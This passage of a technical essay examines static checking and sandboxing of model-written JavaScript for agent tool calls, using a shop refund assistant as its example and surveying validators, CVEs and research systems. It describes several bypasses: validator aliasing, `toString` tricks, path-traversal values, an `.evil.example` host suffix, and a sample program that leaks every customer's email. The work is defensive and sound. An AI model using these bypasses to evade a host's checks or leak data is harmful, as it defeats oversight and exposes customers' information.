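The pmcp-code-mode library also restricts the language. According to a comment at the top of its JavaScript validator, the "safe subset" allows `const` and `let`, arrow functions, conditionals, `try`/`catch`, common array methods and calls on `api`, among other things. It blocks `import` and `export`, `eval`, `while` loops, ordinary function declarations, classes, `this`, and `new` except before six built-in names such as `Date` and `Map`.

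The code in version 0.5.0, from April 2026, mostly implements the blocked list. The validator has a function for each kind of node it rejects or counts, and it lets all other kinds pass. The library has since reached version 0.5.3, and pmcp-code-mode's *Changelog* (2026) describes the changes to this file in 0.5.1 as internal cleanup.

Some of its rules guarantee something about the text, and others are guesses:

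| Rule, with default limits | What it guarantees | What it leaves open |
|---|---|---|
| No `while` or `do...while`, `this`, `delete` or generators | The program contains none of them. | Other ways to the same effect, such as a function that keeps calling itself |
| At most 100 statements, 10 loops and 10 levels of nested blocks | The program is fairly small. | How long it runs |
| At most 50 API calls | At most 50 places in the text call a web method on `api` directly. | How many calls those places make during a run |
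| Loops should have a limit | Nothing. The validator judges by the loop's appearance. | Loops that never end |
| No banned fields in the output | Nothing. The library compares the banned fields with a comment in the program. | Output that the comment doesn't mention |

The validator's loop rule can miss unlimited loops. It counts a `for...of` loop as limited if it runs over the result of `slice`, as in `orders.slice(0, 10)`. It doesn't check the arguments, so `orders.slice()`, which copies the whole list, also counts. It treats every plain `for` loop as "bounded by definition", although `for (;;)` runs forever. A `for...of` loop without `slice` produces only a warning, so the shop's original program would pass.

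The check on output depends on the model accurately declaring what its program returns. The model writes the declaration in an `@returns` comment, which the library searches for banned fields. The check would catch a password field listed in the comment, but a program can return fields that its comment leaves out.

The forbidden list also has predictable gaps. The validator rejects class declarations but accepts class expressions, such as `const A = class {}`. It rejects the `import` statement but has no rule for the `import()` expression, which loads a module while the program runs. It accepts JavaScript up to the 2022 edition, so it parses `api?.refund(r)`, but it doesn't record this API call because it checks only ordinary calls.

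Another gap directly affects a shop like this one. Programs can call `api` with web methods such as `api.get` and `api.post`, or with named operations such as `api.refund`. The validator rightly rejects any named operation that isn't on its permitted list, but it doesn't include named operations in the calls it records and counts. The limit of 50 therefore never applies to them, and the validator marks the program as read-only because it finds no recorded call that writes anything. A host that uses named operations needs to classify the program by their names instead.

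These gaps matter less because the library runs the code in its own executor rather than an ordinary JavaScript engine. According to pmcp-code-mode's *Deferred Improvements* (2026), the library parses the code again and compiles it into steps for that executor. The compiler in effect imposes a permitted list, since a construct with no corresponding step cannot run. The executor also limits how many times a loop can repeat. Since version 0.3.0, the default policy refuses every script until the developer supplies a policy that allows it. The compiler and the policy probably do more for security than the validator's list of bad constructs.

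### AgentScript and NCP

AgentScript, the JavaScript subset used by the sandbox enclave-vm, is closer to a permitted list. Socket's *@enclave-vm/ast* page documents a checker that allows `for` and `for...of` loops and arrow functions, and blocks `while`, `do...while` and `for...in`. All operations go through one function, `callTool`, which takes a tool's name as its first argument. The checker can require that name to be fixed text and compare it with a list, so an AgentScript version of the shop could permit `callTool("refund", ...)` and reject any program that assembles the name from pieces.

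AgentScript also has a list of permitted globals, the names a program can use without declaring them. At the strictest level, these are `callTool`, three constants and seven standard objects, such as `Math`, `JSON` and `Object`. But permitting an object also permits everything reachable through it. `Object` has functions that can change how other objects behave, so the documentation lists `Object.setPrototypeOf` among the attacks the package blocks. A stricter list would permit `Object.keys` but not `Object` itself.

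The limits on AgentScript programs apply at runtime. The defaults in version 2.7.0 are 100 tool calls, 10,000 loop iterations and five seconds, according to Pkg Stats' *enclave-vm* page. The tool-call limit counts the calls a program makes as it runs, whereas pmcp-code-mode's validator counts the places in the program's text where calls appear.

The same page reports more than 1,900 passing security tests. But *CVE-2026-25533 Detail*, published in February 2026 in the US government's National Vulnerability Database (NVD), describes a vulnerability in all versions before 2.10.1, including 2.7.0. A program could get past the syntax-tree check by computing property names at run time, and it could reach the function constructor through host objects. GitLab's *@enclave-vm/core is vulnerable to Sandbox Escape* reports a flaw in a related package that let an attacker escape the sandbox and run code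 remotely in versions before 2.11.1.

The checker's current documentation lists computed property access, names built at run time and destructured property names as known limitations "inherent to any static analyzer". This is true of a checker that accepts these constructs and tries to work out which property they reach. A checker can instead reject every `x[e]` unless `e` is a fixed number, and compare each name in a destructuring pattern with its permitted list, because those names normally appear in the code. This would remove these limitations, but the checker would also reject some code that uses only permitted operations.

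NCP, another system that runs model-written JavaScript with access to tools, relies more on forbidden names. Its checker blocks globals such as `eval`, `process`, `Reflect` and `Proxy`, properties such as `__proto__` and `constructor`, and Node.js modules for files, processes and networking. The checker's tests, on Glama's *code analyzer.test* page, show how such a list grows, with separate cases for the same forbidden property written after a dot, in brackets as an ordinary string, and in brackets as a template string.

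For packages, NCP uses a permitted list instead of a forbidden one. A program can load only the fifteen packages on the list unless the user approves another, and it must give each package's name as fixed text, so it's easy to see which packages it uses. But checking the program doesn't check the code inside those packages, and a package such as lodash contains far more code than the model's program. To back up its forbidden list, NCP also freezes the built-in prototypes and isolates the running program.

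### The n8n flaws

A forbidden list can fail when attackers study it closely, as happened with the workflow tool n8n. Its users can put short JavaScript expressions into a workflow, and n8n checks each expression before evaluating it on its server. In December 2025, n8n disclosed a flaw, CVE-2025-68613, that let anyone with permission to edit workflows bypass these checks and run commands on the server. The fix blocked the forms of bypass that the company knew about.

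In January 2026 the security company JFrog disclosed another escape, CVE-2026-1470. It relied on `with`, an obsolete statement that the checks didn't handle properly. In February n8n patched CVE-2026-25049, which covered further expressions that got around the December fix. Each patch was correct for the forms it addressed but left another form unblocked.

A workflow expression usually needs little more than field names, arithmetic and some string functions, so a list of permitted operations looks feasible. But n8n's customers already have workflows, and a strict list would break some of them. A shop that is introducing an assistant has no old programs to break, so it can easily start with a strict list.

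### STELP

*STELP* (Shinde, Wadhwa and colleagues, 2026) reports some measurements of a permitted list, though for Python. A developer specifies which parts of Python's grammar a program may use, and which functions, packages and tools. STELP parses the program and compares its syntax tree with this specification. Like a transpiler, it then translates the program into other source code, in which a separate function handles each kind of node in the tree, and runs that code instead of the model's own. These functions add controls such as timeouts, retries and checks on the arguments of tool calls.

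The translation adds little time. The median program took 0.19 milliseconds longer than in ordinary Python. The mean increase was 4.93 milliseconds because a few programs slowed down much more, the worst by 520 milliseconds. STELP also produced the correct output for all 361 programs in a correctness test, although Shinde and colleagues had selected programs that fitted the configuration.

The safety test compared STELP with CodeShield, a tool from Meta that searches for known insecure patterns. The test programs came from 164 harmless solutions to programming exercises, into which a model inserted dangerous fragments such as endless loops or calls to `eval`. Human reviewers removed unsuitable examples, leaving 470 unsafe programs that covered twelve kinds of weakness.

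| | Unsafe programs blocked | Harmless programs allowed |
|---|---|---|
| STELP | 100% | 98.1% |
| CodeShield | 68% | 93% |

CodeShield missed about 150 of the 470. Most of STELP's blocks came from function calls or imports that weren't on its permitted list, so it didn't need to detect the particular weakness, which is the advantage one would expect from such a list.

However, the comparison favors STELP. Shinde and colleagues wrote the configuration by hand as the minimum that would let the benchmark's harmless programs run, then measured how many of those programs it allowed. The 98.1% is therefore little evidence of how it would handle new programs. The perfect block rate is also weaker evidence than it looks, because nobody tried to write an attack using only the permitted functions. In the shop, such an attack could be a call to `api.sendEmail` with the wrong recipient.

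STELP has another drawback for irreversible operations, because it enforces part of its configuration one statement at a time while the program runs. In one of its examples, a program looks something up on Wikipedia, adds a record to a database and then tries to open a network connection, which is forbidden. STELP stops the program at that line, after the database has changed.

### ADsafe and Caja

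Web developers had to deal with untrusted JavaScript long before language models wrote any. A news site might carry another company's advertisement, and the advertisement's program, or widget, would run with the same privileges as the site's own code. In Douglas Crockford's ADsafe, a static checker called JSLint rejected any widget that used JavaScript outside a permitted subset. A run-time library, `adsafe.js`, then gave the accepted widgets restricted access to the page. It handed them wrappers instead of real page elements, and the wrappers' methods checked each request.

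Neither part is safe alone. The library relies on JSLint to keep widgets from reaching inside the wrappers, and JSLint relies on the library never to hand over a real element. Politz and colleagues turned this dependence into a proof. They described everything a widget may hold with a single type, Widget. In outline:

```
a Widget is   a number, string, true, false, null or undefined
         or   an object whose banned fields are out of reach
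              and whose other fields hold Widgets
         or   a function that takes Widgets and returns a Widget
```

The full type makes a few exceptions for the library's own wrappers. Real page elements aren't Widgets, and neither is the window.

The proof has three parts. First, every variable and expression in a widget that passes JSLint must have the type Widget. Second, every function that the library offers must accept any Widgets as arguments and return a Widget. A type checker confirms this by examining the library's code. Third, running a step of the program must preserve the types, which Politz and colleagues proved for their type system. A widget therefore never obtains a real page element or loads new code.

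The division of labour is useful because the type checker has to go through the library only once, which takes 20 seconds. After that, each new widget needs only the static check.

Politz and colleagues report some gaps in their proof. They couldn't verify eleven of the library's 1,800 lines, and they had to rewrite some others in a form the type checker could handle. They assumed that the surrounding page doesn't alter JavaScript's built-in prototypes, though pages often do. They tested the connection between JSLint and the type Widget with examples instead of proving it, because JSLint had no specification apart from its code.

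One error they found was in that connection. JSLint was supposed to ban field names that begin and end with underscores, because the library kept real page elements in such fields, but it missed names in quotation marks. A widget could use a quoted field name to build a fake wrapper and make the library pass it a real element. Crockford had offered a reward to anyone who got a malicious widget past JSLint's ADsafe checks, and he agreed that they had earned it.

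Several library functions wrongly assumed that their arguments were strings. One searched a style setting for the letters `url`, to keep widgets from loading outside resources, and then applied the setting. A widget could supply an object whose `toString` method returned something harmless during the search and an address when the setting was applied. Crockford added a check that the argument is a string, and now uses it in 18 functions.

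The type checker also flagged a function that let a widget read any property of a style object by name, including a built-in prototype that the whole page shares. A widget could alter that prototype and so interfere with the page and other widgets. Crockford fixed the function, but then pointed out that two widgets could still exchange messages by attaching data to a built-in array method, and he withdrew the claim that ADsafe keeps widgets from communicating.

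The same errors as in the library could occur in the shop. Suppose the host checks that `amount` is at most 50, then converts `amount` to a number again when it makes the payment. An object that converts to 20 the first time and 5,000 the second would pass the check. The host can prevent this by first copying the arguments into plain data, such as JSON text, and then checking and using only the copy.

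Google's Caja covered more of JavaScript than ADsafe did. It rewrote developers' code to insert calls to run-time checks, which ADsafe left developers to insert themselves. For example, it replaced `obj[name]` with a call to a function that examined the name first. This let people write something close to ordinary JavaScript, but it made Caja much larger. Outside experts who reviewed Caja at Google's request in 2008 found it "hard to review", partly because no document listed the properties that the code had to maintain and where it enforced them. Caja's successor, Hardened JavaScript, relies mainly on changes to the run-time environment, which a later section covers.

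This is a reason to base a new checker on a small language with a written definition. ADsafe's language was small, but until Politz and colleagues wrote a definition of it, nobody could tell whether JSLint was enforcing the right language.

### A subset for the shop

The shop's definition can fit on half a page:

```
Statements     const name = expression
               await api.operation({ ... })
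               if / else
               for (const name of list.slice(0, n)) { ... },
                    where n is a whole number written in the program
               return expression

Expressions    numbers, strings, true, false, null
               names declared earlier in the program
               x.field, where field is on the permitted list
               + - * /   < <= > >= === !==   && || !
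               objects and lists, containing no functions
               await api.operation({ ... })
               list.filter(f), list.map(f) and list.slice(a, b),
                    where f is an arrow function written in place
                    that makes no api calls

api            only in the form api.operation({ ... })

Everything else is rejected.
```

Some of these rules depend on each other. The limit on loops works only if `slice` is JavaScript's own array method, because a program that could replace it with another function could return a list of any length. The subset allows neither assignment to properties nor functions inside objects, so a program can't replace `slice` or define a `toString` method that returns different values on different calls. The host must also return only plain data and leave JavaScript's built-in methods unchanged.

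The assistant's program fits once it has the two limits it lacked, on the number of refunds and on the size of each:

```js
const orders = await api.listOrders({ from: "2026-11-23", to: "2026-11-29" });
const late = orders.filter(o => o.deliveredOn > o.promisedOn);
const small = late.filter(o => o.total > 0 && o.total <= 50);
for (const order of small.slice(0, 10)) {
  await api.refund({ orderId: order.id, amount: order.total });
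  await api.sendEmail({
    to: order.customerEmail,
    subject: "Refund for order " + order.id,
    body: "Your order arrived late, so we have refunded it in full."
  });
}
return { late: late.length, small: small.length };
```

The checker can establish from this text that the program makes at most ten refunds. If only four refunds remain for the task, the model must write `slice(0, 4)`. The program returns both totals so that the assistant can report any late orders it left out because they cost more than 50 or because the limit was reached. The checker can't determine whether `listOrders` might return the same order twice, so the host has to enforce the limit of one refund per order.

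### What the restrictions cost

This task loses nothing important under the subset, but other common tasks would. Suppose `listOrders` returned a hundred orders at a time, with a marker for the next page. Programmers normally fetch all the pages with a `while` loop that runs until there is no marker, but the subset doesn't allow such loops. The host could instead collect the pages inside `listOrders`.

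Adding up refunds for each customer is also awkward, because the usual way is to keep totals in an object and write `totals[o.customerEmail]`, a computed property access whose name comes from the data. The shop could offer a helper function that groups a list by a named field. Each such helper becomes part of the trusted code, so it must be written to handle hostile arguments, as ADsafe's library should have been.

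The subset can also make programs slower. A program in the full language could send all ten emails at once with `Promise.all`, whereas one in the subset waits for each email before sending the next. AgentScript similarly blocks `Promise`, along with `Map`, `Set` and regular expressions.

safescript, a small language for agents that looks like JavaScript, gives up still more to make analysis easier. It has no loops or recursion, only `map`, `filter` and `reduce` over finite lists, so every program finishes. A program has to write the name of each secret it reads and each server it contacts as fixed text. The analyser can then list them all in advance, along with the data that may flow between them. The documentation calls this analysis "exact, not heuristic", but for a conditional the analyser combines what both branches might do, so it can report a flow that never happens. The documentation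 also concedes that the language can't express a program that sorts a list.

A language as strict as safescript would suit a shop whose tasks mostly fetch data and pass it on. Its practical disadvantage is that models have been trained on vast amounts of JavaScript and probably very little safescript. A subset of JavaScript makes use of that training. The shop can start with the half-page definition and add a construct when useful programs need it, once somebody has written a rule for it and considered how it interacts with the others.

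## Listing the operations a program can perform

A program that fits the shop's subset can still refund the wrong amount or send a hundred emails. To rule this out, the checker lists every operation the program could perform, with the values each argument might have and the most times the call could run. It then compares the list with the declared scope.

### The procedure

```
check(text, scope):
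    parse the text into a syntax tree
    link every name in the tree to its declaration
    reject if the tree contains anything outside the safe subset

    for each appearance of the host's api:
        reject unless it is part of a call api.operation({ ... })
        arguments = the values each argument could have
        calls     = the most times this call could run
        add (operation, arguments, calls) to the list

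    for each operation on the list:
        reject if the scope doesn't permit it
        reject if an argument could fall outside the scope
        reject if its calls could add up to more than the scope allows

    accept
```

The checker has to link names to declarations because JavaScript lets an inner block reuse a name from outside it:

```js
const amount = 20;
if (late.length > 5) {
  const amount = 5000;
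  await api.refund({ orderId: "A-1001", amount: amount });
}
```

This program refunds 5,000. A checker that looked up `amount` by its spelling alone might find the 20 and accept the program. Linking avoids this mistake by following JavaScript's rule that the nearest enclosing declaration applies. It also lets the checker determine that `api` in `orders.filter(api => api.total > 20)` refers to an order and not to the host API. The shop could instead reject any program that declares the same name twice, since a model can easily pick another name.

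### Aliases

An alias is a second name or reference for the same object or function, such as `give` in `const give = api.refund`. A checker that recognises only the direct form `api.operation(...)` is sound only if it rejects every other use of `api`.

It's easy to write the first half of this rule and forget the second. In version 0.5.0, pmcp-code-mode's validator looks for methods called directly on `api`, and it neither records nor rejects these lines:

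```js
const send = api.post;
await send("/refunds", { orderId: "A-1001", amount: 5000 });
```

It therefore marks this program as read-only, and whether the refund goes through depends on the library's executor.

The full rule rejects the program at its first line, where `api` appears outside a direct call. It also rejects other ways of creating an alias, such as putting `api` in an array or passing it to a function, without having to list them. The program receives the host API under a single name, so every alias must start where that name appears in the text. If each appearance is part of a direct call, and the calls return only plain data, no variable can hold `api` or one of its functions. This holds only if the subset blocks other routes to the host API, such as the global object.

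The rule also rejects harmless programs that begin with `const { refund, sendEmail } = api`, but a model can easily write the names in full.

### Following functions from name to name

A checker that accepts aliases has to follow them. Pointer analysis works out which objects and functions each variable or property might hold. A call graph records which functions each call could reach. For JavaScript, neither can be complete without the other, as this program shows:

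```js
const run = (f, x) => f(x);
await run(api.listOrders, week);
await run(api.refund, { orderId: "A-1001", amount: 20 });
```

To find out what `f(x)` calls, the analysis needs to know what `f` holds, which depends on the calls that reach `run`. It therefore starts from the facts that are plain in the text and applies its rules until they yield nothing new:

```
run may hold the arrow function
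    so both calls to run may reach it
    so f may hold listOrders or refund,
       and x may hold week or the refund's details
    so f(x) may call either function with either argument
```

The last line includes a refund whose argument is `week`, which has no amount. The program never makes this call, but a checker that relied on the analysis would reject the program. A more precise analysis treats each call to `run` separately, which takes more code and computation.

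*GATEKEEPER* (Guarnieri and Livshits, 2009) presents an early system of this kind, built to check widgets before a site such as Live.com published them. The paper describes its pointer analysis as the first for JavaScript. GateKeeper turns a widget into a database of facts, such as "this variable may hold that function", and works out the call graph and what each variable may point to together. Each policy is a short query on the result. A query to ban pop-up boxes, for example, finds the built-in function `alert` and reports every call that might reach it under any name.

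GateKeeper rejects widgets that use `eval` and a few similar features. Rejecting every `a[index]` with an unknown index would have ruled out 39% of the widgets from the Windows Vista sidebar, so GateKeeper inserts a run-time check there that compares the property's name with a list of forbidden strings.

As printed in the paper, this check can be bypassed because it uses `===`, which doesn't convert its operands. An object whose `toString` method returns `"eval"` isn't equal to the string `"eval"`, so it passes the check, but JavaScript converts it to that string when it reads the property. ADsafe's library had much the same flaw. Guarnieri and Livshits acknowledge that it is difficult to cover every case a malicious widget might exploit.

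The GateKeeper paper tested nine policies on a collection of 8,379 widgets, about 6,500 of which used only the part of JavaScript that GateKeeper could handle. GateKeeper found 1,341 real violations in 684 widgets. It also raised 113 false alarms, all in two widgets and nearly all because of how it treated arrays in one file. Most widgets took less than four seconds to check on a desktop computer of the time.

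These results are encouraging, but most of the policies concerned whether a widget used a particular function or object. GateKeeper doesn't model numbers or strings, so it could enforce a ban on `api.refund` but not a limit of 50. It also needs a description of every built-in function that might pass an object along. Guarnieri and Livshits generated a first version automatically and corrected it by hand, which they call error-prone. In one of their examples, a program adds an element to a web page and then retrieves it through the page's list of children. If the description leaves out that connection, the analysis misses an alias.

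Later work shows how much effort it takes to analyse nearly all of JavaScript soundly. *JSAI* (Kashyap, Dewey and colleagues, 2014) uses abstract interpretation, which in effect runs a program on descriptions of values, such as "some number" or "one of these two functions". It tracks pointers, strings, numbers and control flow together, because each helps with the others. For instance, if the string analysis can work out a property's name, the pointer analysis can determine which function the program reads. Kashyap and colleagues tested their model of JavaScript against the SpiderMonkey engine on more than a million programs, most of them randomly generated. JSAI still covers an old edition of the language and leaves out `eval`.

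Following a simple alias is now routine. CodeQL's JavaScript library treats both `o.m(...)` and `tmp = o.m; tmp(...)` as calls to the method `m`.

### Capability analysis of npm libraries

In *Defensive Capability Analysis for JavaScript Libraries*, Xu and Møller (2026) aim to find every place where an npm package for Node.js could use a capability, meaning the ability to do something sensitive such as read a file, use the network or start a process. They keep pointer analysis manageable by following only the objects that matter for security.

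The analysis starts from a list of sensitive functions and objects, such as `eval` and the function that reads files. It adds any object a program could use to reach one of these, such as `global`, which holds JavaScript's built-in functions. It then follows these objects through assignments, property reads and calls to built-in functions, and ignores everything else.

If the code uses a sensitive function that the analysis has followed, the analysis makes a direct report, which gives the exact line. If a tracked object goes somewhere the analysis doesn't follow, the analysis makes an indirect report, which lists everything the program could do with that object from then on. For example, `x.f = eval` stores `eval` in a property, and the analysis would have to know every object `x` could be to find where `eval` might be used next. Instead, it reports that the program may execute code at some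 later point, which covers every such use but doesn't locate any of them.

Three features of JavaScript would undermine this guarantee, and Xu and Møller block them at run time:

| How a program could get around the analysis | What the run-time protection does |
|---|---|
| Every function inherits a `constructor` property that leads to `Function`, which turns text into code. A program can reach it as `f[e]` if `e` happens to be `"constructor"`. | Replaces the inherited constructor with a function that throws an error |
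| In JavaScript's older, non-strict mode, a function called on its own receives the global object as `this`. | Rewrites functions that use `this` so that they don't receive the real global object |
| A program can add a method to a prototype that a sensitive object inherits from. The method then receives that object as `this`. | Freezes the prototype, or gives the object a frozen copy |

Covering these cases in the static analysis too would have meant treating many ordinary uses of `this` and of computed properties as suspicious. Harmless packages seldom rely on the blocked features. Xu and Møller ran the tests of 3,682 software projects with the protection on, and it rejected something in only 67 of them, so 98.2% were compatible. Most of the 67 failures came from tools for testing or building software.

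At least 72.9% of the packages used no sensitive capability, so an auditor could skip them. This figure counts each shared library once. Of the 5,685 popular packages in the sample, 59.4% used no sensitive capability, either directly or through their dependencies.

The analysis also found sensitive capabilities in 1,309 of 1,311 known malicious packages (99.8%). The other two reached the `Function` constructor in a way that the run-time protection blocks. The analysis detects what code can do, not whether it is malicious. It also reported capabilities in about 40% of the popular packages, so it can reduce the number of packages a person has to review but can't identify which ones are malicious.

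For comparison, Xu and Møller built a version that only matches patterns in the syntax tree. It recognises `eval()` written out in full, and makes an indirect report whenever a sensitive object is used in any other way. With the run-time protection on, this version gives the same guarantee as the pointer analysis. They checked 540 reports by hand to estimate the share that were correct.

| | Syntax patterns | Pointer analysis |
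|---|---|---|
| Reports that were correct | 42.4% | 70.2% |
| Modules with an indirect report | 7,539 | 2,437 |
| Packages analysed within 20 seconds | 99.0% | 99.0% |

Pointer analysis was much more precise and took no noticeable extra time. Conventional pointer analysis takes more computation, but this version tracks few objects and stops tracking them early.

### What carries over to short programs

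The shop's rule for `api` is the strictest form of the syntax version. `api` is the only sensitive object, and the checker rejects any use of it that it doesn't recognise instead of giving an indirect report.

Indirect reports on a library take a lot of time because somebody has to read the code. Xu and Møller spent more than four of their six hours of auditing on the indirect cases. The shop's model can rewrite a rejected program, so the shop gains much less from greater precision.

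Both methods should be almost instant on ten lines, so speed hardly matters either. The main drawback of pointer analysis is that the shop's checker needs more code. It needs rules for each way a value can move and a description of each built-in function, and an error in any of them could let a forbidden operation through. The direct-call rule is short enough for one person to review thoroughly. A new checker should probably start with that rule and add pointer analysis only if useful programs keep failing the check.

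The three features blocked at run time can also be excluded from the permitted subset. The shop's subset has no `this`, no computed property names and no assignment to properties. The host can still freeze the prototypes in case the checker has a bug.

Many of the false alarms Xu and Møller report came from `global`, because code that passes it around for an innocent reason could in theory use any of the powerful functions it holds. Only about 10% of the indirect reports of code execution were correct. A host can avoid this problem by giving the program one small object with three functions instead of `global`.

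The percentages don't apply to model-written scripts, which look nothing like npm libraries. The analysis also doesn't cover amounts or how often a program makes a call. Any useful program in the shop will call `api.refund`, so the checker has to work out how much it refunds and how often.

### What values an argument can have

The checker works out the possible values of an expression from its parts. A literal such as `20` has only one possible value, while a field such as `order.total` can have any value the host might return. If two numbers are each between 0 and 50, their sum is between 0 and 100.

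Kashyap and colleagues designed their analyser, JSAI, to track a number only while it has one known value, and otherwise to record only that it is a number. They made this part replaceable, so someone could add ranges. *From Language Models to Control Policies* (2026) describes 29 checks on the syntax trees of model-written control programs. Three check for outputs outside fixed ranges, such as 0 to 500, and two check for divisions that could produce infinity or NaN.

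NaN, short for "not a number", is the value JavaScript gives when arithmetic fails. It causes trouble in a common way of enforcing a limit. Suppose the shop adds `Math.min`, which returns the smallest of its arguments, to its subset, and the model writes:

```js
for (const order of late.slice(0, 10)) {
  await api.refund({ orderId: order.id, amount: Math.min(order.total, 50) });
}
```

The amount can't exceed 50, but it could be negative, because `Math.min(-20, 50)` is -20. It could also be NaN if `total` is missing. A host that only checks whether the amount is more than 50 would accept NaN, because `NaN > 50` is false. If the host first copies the arguments as JSON, NaN becomes `null`, and a payment service might treat a null amount as a request to refund the whole order.

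The checker therefore rejects this program. One more test is enough to make it pass:

```js
for (const order of late.slice(0, 10)) {
  const amount = Math.min(order.total, 50);
  if (amount > 0) {
    await api.refund({ orderId: order.id, amount: amount });
  }
}
```

Inside the `if`, the amount is above 0 and at most 50. The test excludes NaN because `NaN > 0` is false. `amount` is a constant, so its value can't change between the test and the refund.

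A model might instead write the opposite test, `if (amount <= 0) { return null; }`, and put the refund after it. The refund can then run with an amount that is above 0 or `NaN`, because `NaN <= 0` is false. A sound checker keeps `NaN` as a possible value until the program can continue only if a test such as `amount > 0` is true.

The shop's earlier program instead filtered the orders with `o.total > 0 && o.total <= 50`. The checker can treat this condition as true of every order in the filtered list, because the subset gives a program no way to change an order afterwards. But the condition doesn't prove that `total` is a number. JavaScript converts the text `"20"` to a number for the comparison, so an order with that total passes the filter, and the program sends the text to `api.refund`. The host can prevent this by checking the types of everything `listOrders` returns. `Math.min` doesn't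 have this problem, because it always returns a number.

The two programs also treat an order of 80 differently. The filter excludes it, whereas `Math.min` limits the refund to 50. Both programs fit the scope, so checking them doesn't show which result the member of staff wanted.

### How many calls a program can make

The checker finds the most times a call could run by moving up the syntax tree from the call and multiplying the limits of the loops that contain it. A call outside any loop runs at most once. A refund in a loop over `orders.slice(0, 10)` runs at most 10 times. If the refund is instead in a second loop of 10 nested inside that one, the limit is 100.

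If the program calls the same operation in several places, the checker adds the counts. Two consecutive loops that each make 10 calls give a total of 20. For an `if` with an `else`, the checker can use the larger of the two branches' counts, because only one branch runs.

The program that passed can issue at most 10 refunds of at most 50 each, so the total is at most 500. If the second loop were inside the first, the total could reach 5,000, and the checker would reject the program because it could make more than ten calls.

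Whether `slice` limits the number of items it returns depends on its exact arguments. `slice(0, 10)` returns at most ten items, but `slice(10)` returns everything after the first ten, and `slice(0, -1)` returns everything except the last. The shop's subset excludes the last two forms because it requires the end of the range to be a whole number written in the program and has no minus sign for negative numbers.

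Multiplying can greatly overestimate the number of calls. Suppose the model wants to handle the refunds day by day:

```js
for (const day of days.slice(0, 7)) {
  for (const order of late.slice(0, 10)) {
    if (order.promisedOn === day) {
      await api.refund({ orderId: order.id, amount: 20 });
    }
  }
}
```

If the days are all different, each order matches at most one of them, and the program makes at most ten refunds. The checker calculates a maximum of 70 refunds and rejects the program. A more sophisticated checker could take the dates into account, but it's easier for the model to write a single loop over the orders.

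Counting during the run avoids this false rejection. Dunkel's system, for example, caps the number of API calls a program can make. But a cap can stop a program partway through, so it's more useful as a backup in case the checker has made a mistake.

### Comparing the list with the scope

For the shop's program with the filter, the finished list looks like this:

| Operation | Arguments | Most calls |
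|---|---|---|
| `listOrders` | `from` is "2026-11-23" and `to` is "2026-11-29" | 1 |
| `refund` | `orderId` is the order's `id`; `amount` is above 0 and at most 50 | 10 |
| `sendEmail` | `to` is the same order's `customerEmail`; `subject` starts with "Refund for order "; `body` is fixed text | 10 |

The amount and the number of calls are within the scope. The scope also requires each email to go to a customer whose order the task has already refunded. The checker can establish this because the email follows the refund in the same pass through the loop and takes its address from the same order. The subset has no `try`/`catch`, so if a refund fails with an error, the program stops before it sends the email. The host must therefore report a failed refund as an error and not as an ordinary result. The host also still has to prevent a second refund for the same order. (Whether private data could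 end up in an email is a separate question, which needs the methods of the next section.)

The list also helps a person who has to approve the task, because "at most ten refunds of up to 50 each" is easier to judge than the code.

However, the list is only as accurate as the shop's understanding of its own functions. *ACaM* (Santra, Kirat and colleagues, 2026) describes a weather tool that also reads a file of credentials and sends them to a server. A checker that examined just the model's program would find only a request for a forecast. ACaM analyses the Python source code of an agent's tools to determine what they can do. A language model adds judgments about meaning but can't override the facts established by static analysis. ACaM marks code it can't resolve as unknown rather than safe. On 24 hand-labelled agents, it scored 98.3% on a measure that counts both missed and false findings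 against it.

A team could run an analysis like this whenever its host functions change. It wouldn't have to repeat the analysis for each program, just as one proof about ADsafe's library covered all widgets.

### Paths built from data

Some hosts give programs general web methods instead of named operations. The program then chooses a path on the server, often by inserting data into a template:

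```js
const info = await api.get(`/orders/${id}/summary`);
```

If `id` comes from data, the checker knows only the fixed pieces of the path. It seems to follow that the request stays under `/orders/`, but it doesn't. Before software sends a request, it usually normalises the path, which includes treating `..` as an instruction to go up one level. The text of the path still begins with `/orders/`, but the server may receive something else:

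| Value of `id` | Path the server receives |
|---|---|
| `A-1001` | `/orders/A-1001/summary` |
| `../customers` | `/customers/summary` |
| `../admin/config?` | `/admin/config` |

In the last row, the question mark turns the rest of the template into a query, so the fixed ending isn't secure either. Searching `id` for two dots doesn't solve the problem, because URL parsers that follow the web standard also read `%2e%2e` as two dots.

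pmcp-code-mode's validator keeps the fixed parts of a template and replaces each inserted value with a placeholder. It then searches the result for sensitive paths such as `/admin`. It wouldn't find one in this template, whatever `id` turned out to be. It does report every path built from a template as a potential issue, but a busy shop would soon learn to ignore that warning.

When a program builds a full web address by adding data to a fixed server name, the fixed part has to include the slash after the name. Without the slash, a program could add data beginning with `.evil.example/` to `https://api.shop.example`, and the request would go to a different server. With the slash, the checker can establish which server the program will contact, but not which path.

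JavaScript's usual remedy, `encodeURIComponent`, encodes slashes and question marks but leaves dots alone. An `id` of `..` would therefore still turn `/orders/../summary` into `/summary`.

It's safer for the host to build the path itself. It could offer `api.getOrderSummary({ orderId: id })`, accept only order numbers made of letters, digits and hyphens, and insert them into a fixed path. The checker can then treat `getOrderSummary` as another named operation. If the host has to accept paths from programs, it should normalise each one, compare the normalised path with the scope, and send exactly that path.

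## Checking where data can go

A program can respect every limit on its operations and still do harm through what it passes from one operation to another. The shop's scope permits both listing orders and emailing refunded customers, so, as noted earlier, it doesn't stop a program from mailing out everyone's address. Such a program might look like this:

```js
const orders = await api.listOrders({ from: "2026-11-23", to: "2026-11-29" });
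const late = orders.filter(o => o.deliveredOn > o.promisedOn && o.total > 0 && o.total <= 50);
const emails = orders.map(o => o.customerEmail);
const text = "This week's customers: " + emails;
for (const order of late.slice(0, 1)) {
  await api.refund({ orderId: order.id, amount: order.total });
  await api.sendEmail({ to: order.customerEmail, subject: "Refund", body: text });
}
```

The program fits the safe subset, makes one refund of at most 50, and sends one email to the customer it refunded. But when JavaScript joins a list to a string with `+`, it writes out the items with commas between them, so the refunded customer receives the address of everyone who ordered that week.

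Running the program in an isolated environment doesn't prevent it from leaking private data. Odersky and colleagues give the example of an agent that reads a private file and then calls a model in the cloud. A sandbox would normally allow both steps, so the agent could send the file's contents to the model.

Data can also cause harm by flowing the other way, from an untrusted source into an important decision. *SPA* (2026), a paper on protecting agents that keep data between requests, distinguishes confidentiality, which concerns where sensitive data may go, from integrity, which concerns what untrusted data may influence. When the shop sends an email, confidentiality mostly concerns the body, because a customer's order should not be sent to a stranger. Integrity mostly concerns the address, because a note typed into an order form should not determine who receives the email.

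### Following data through the program

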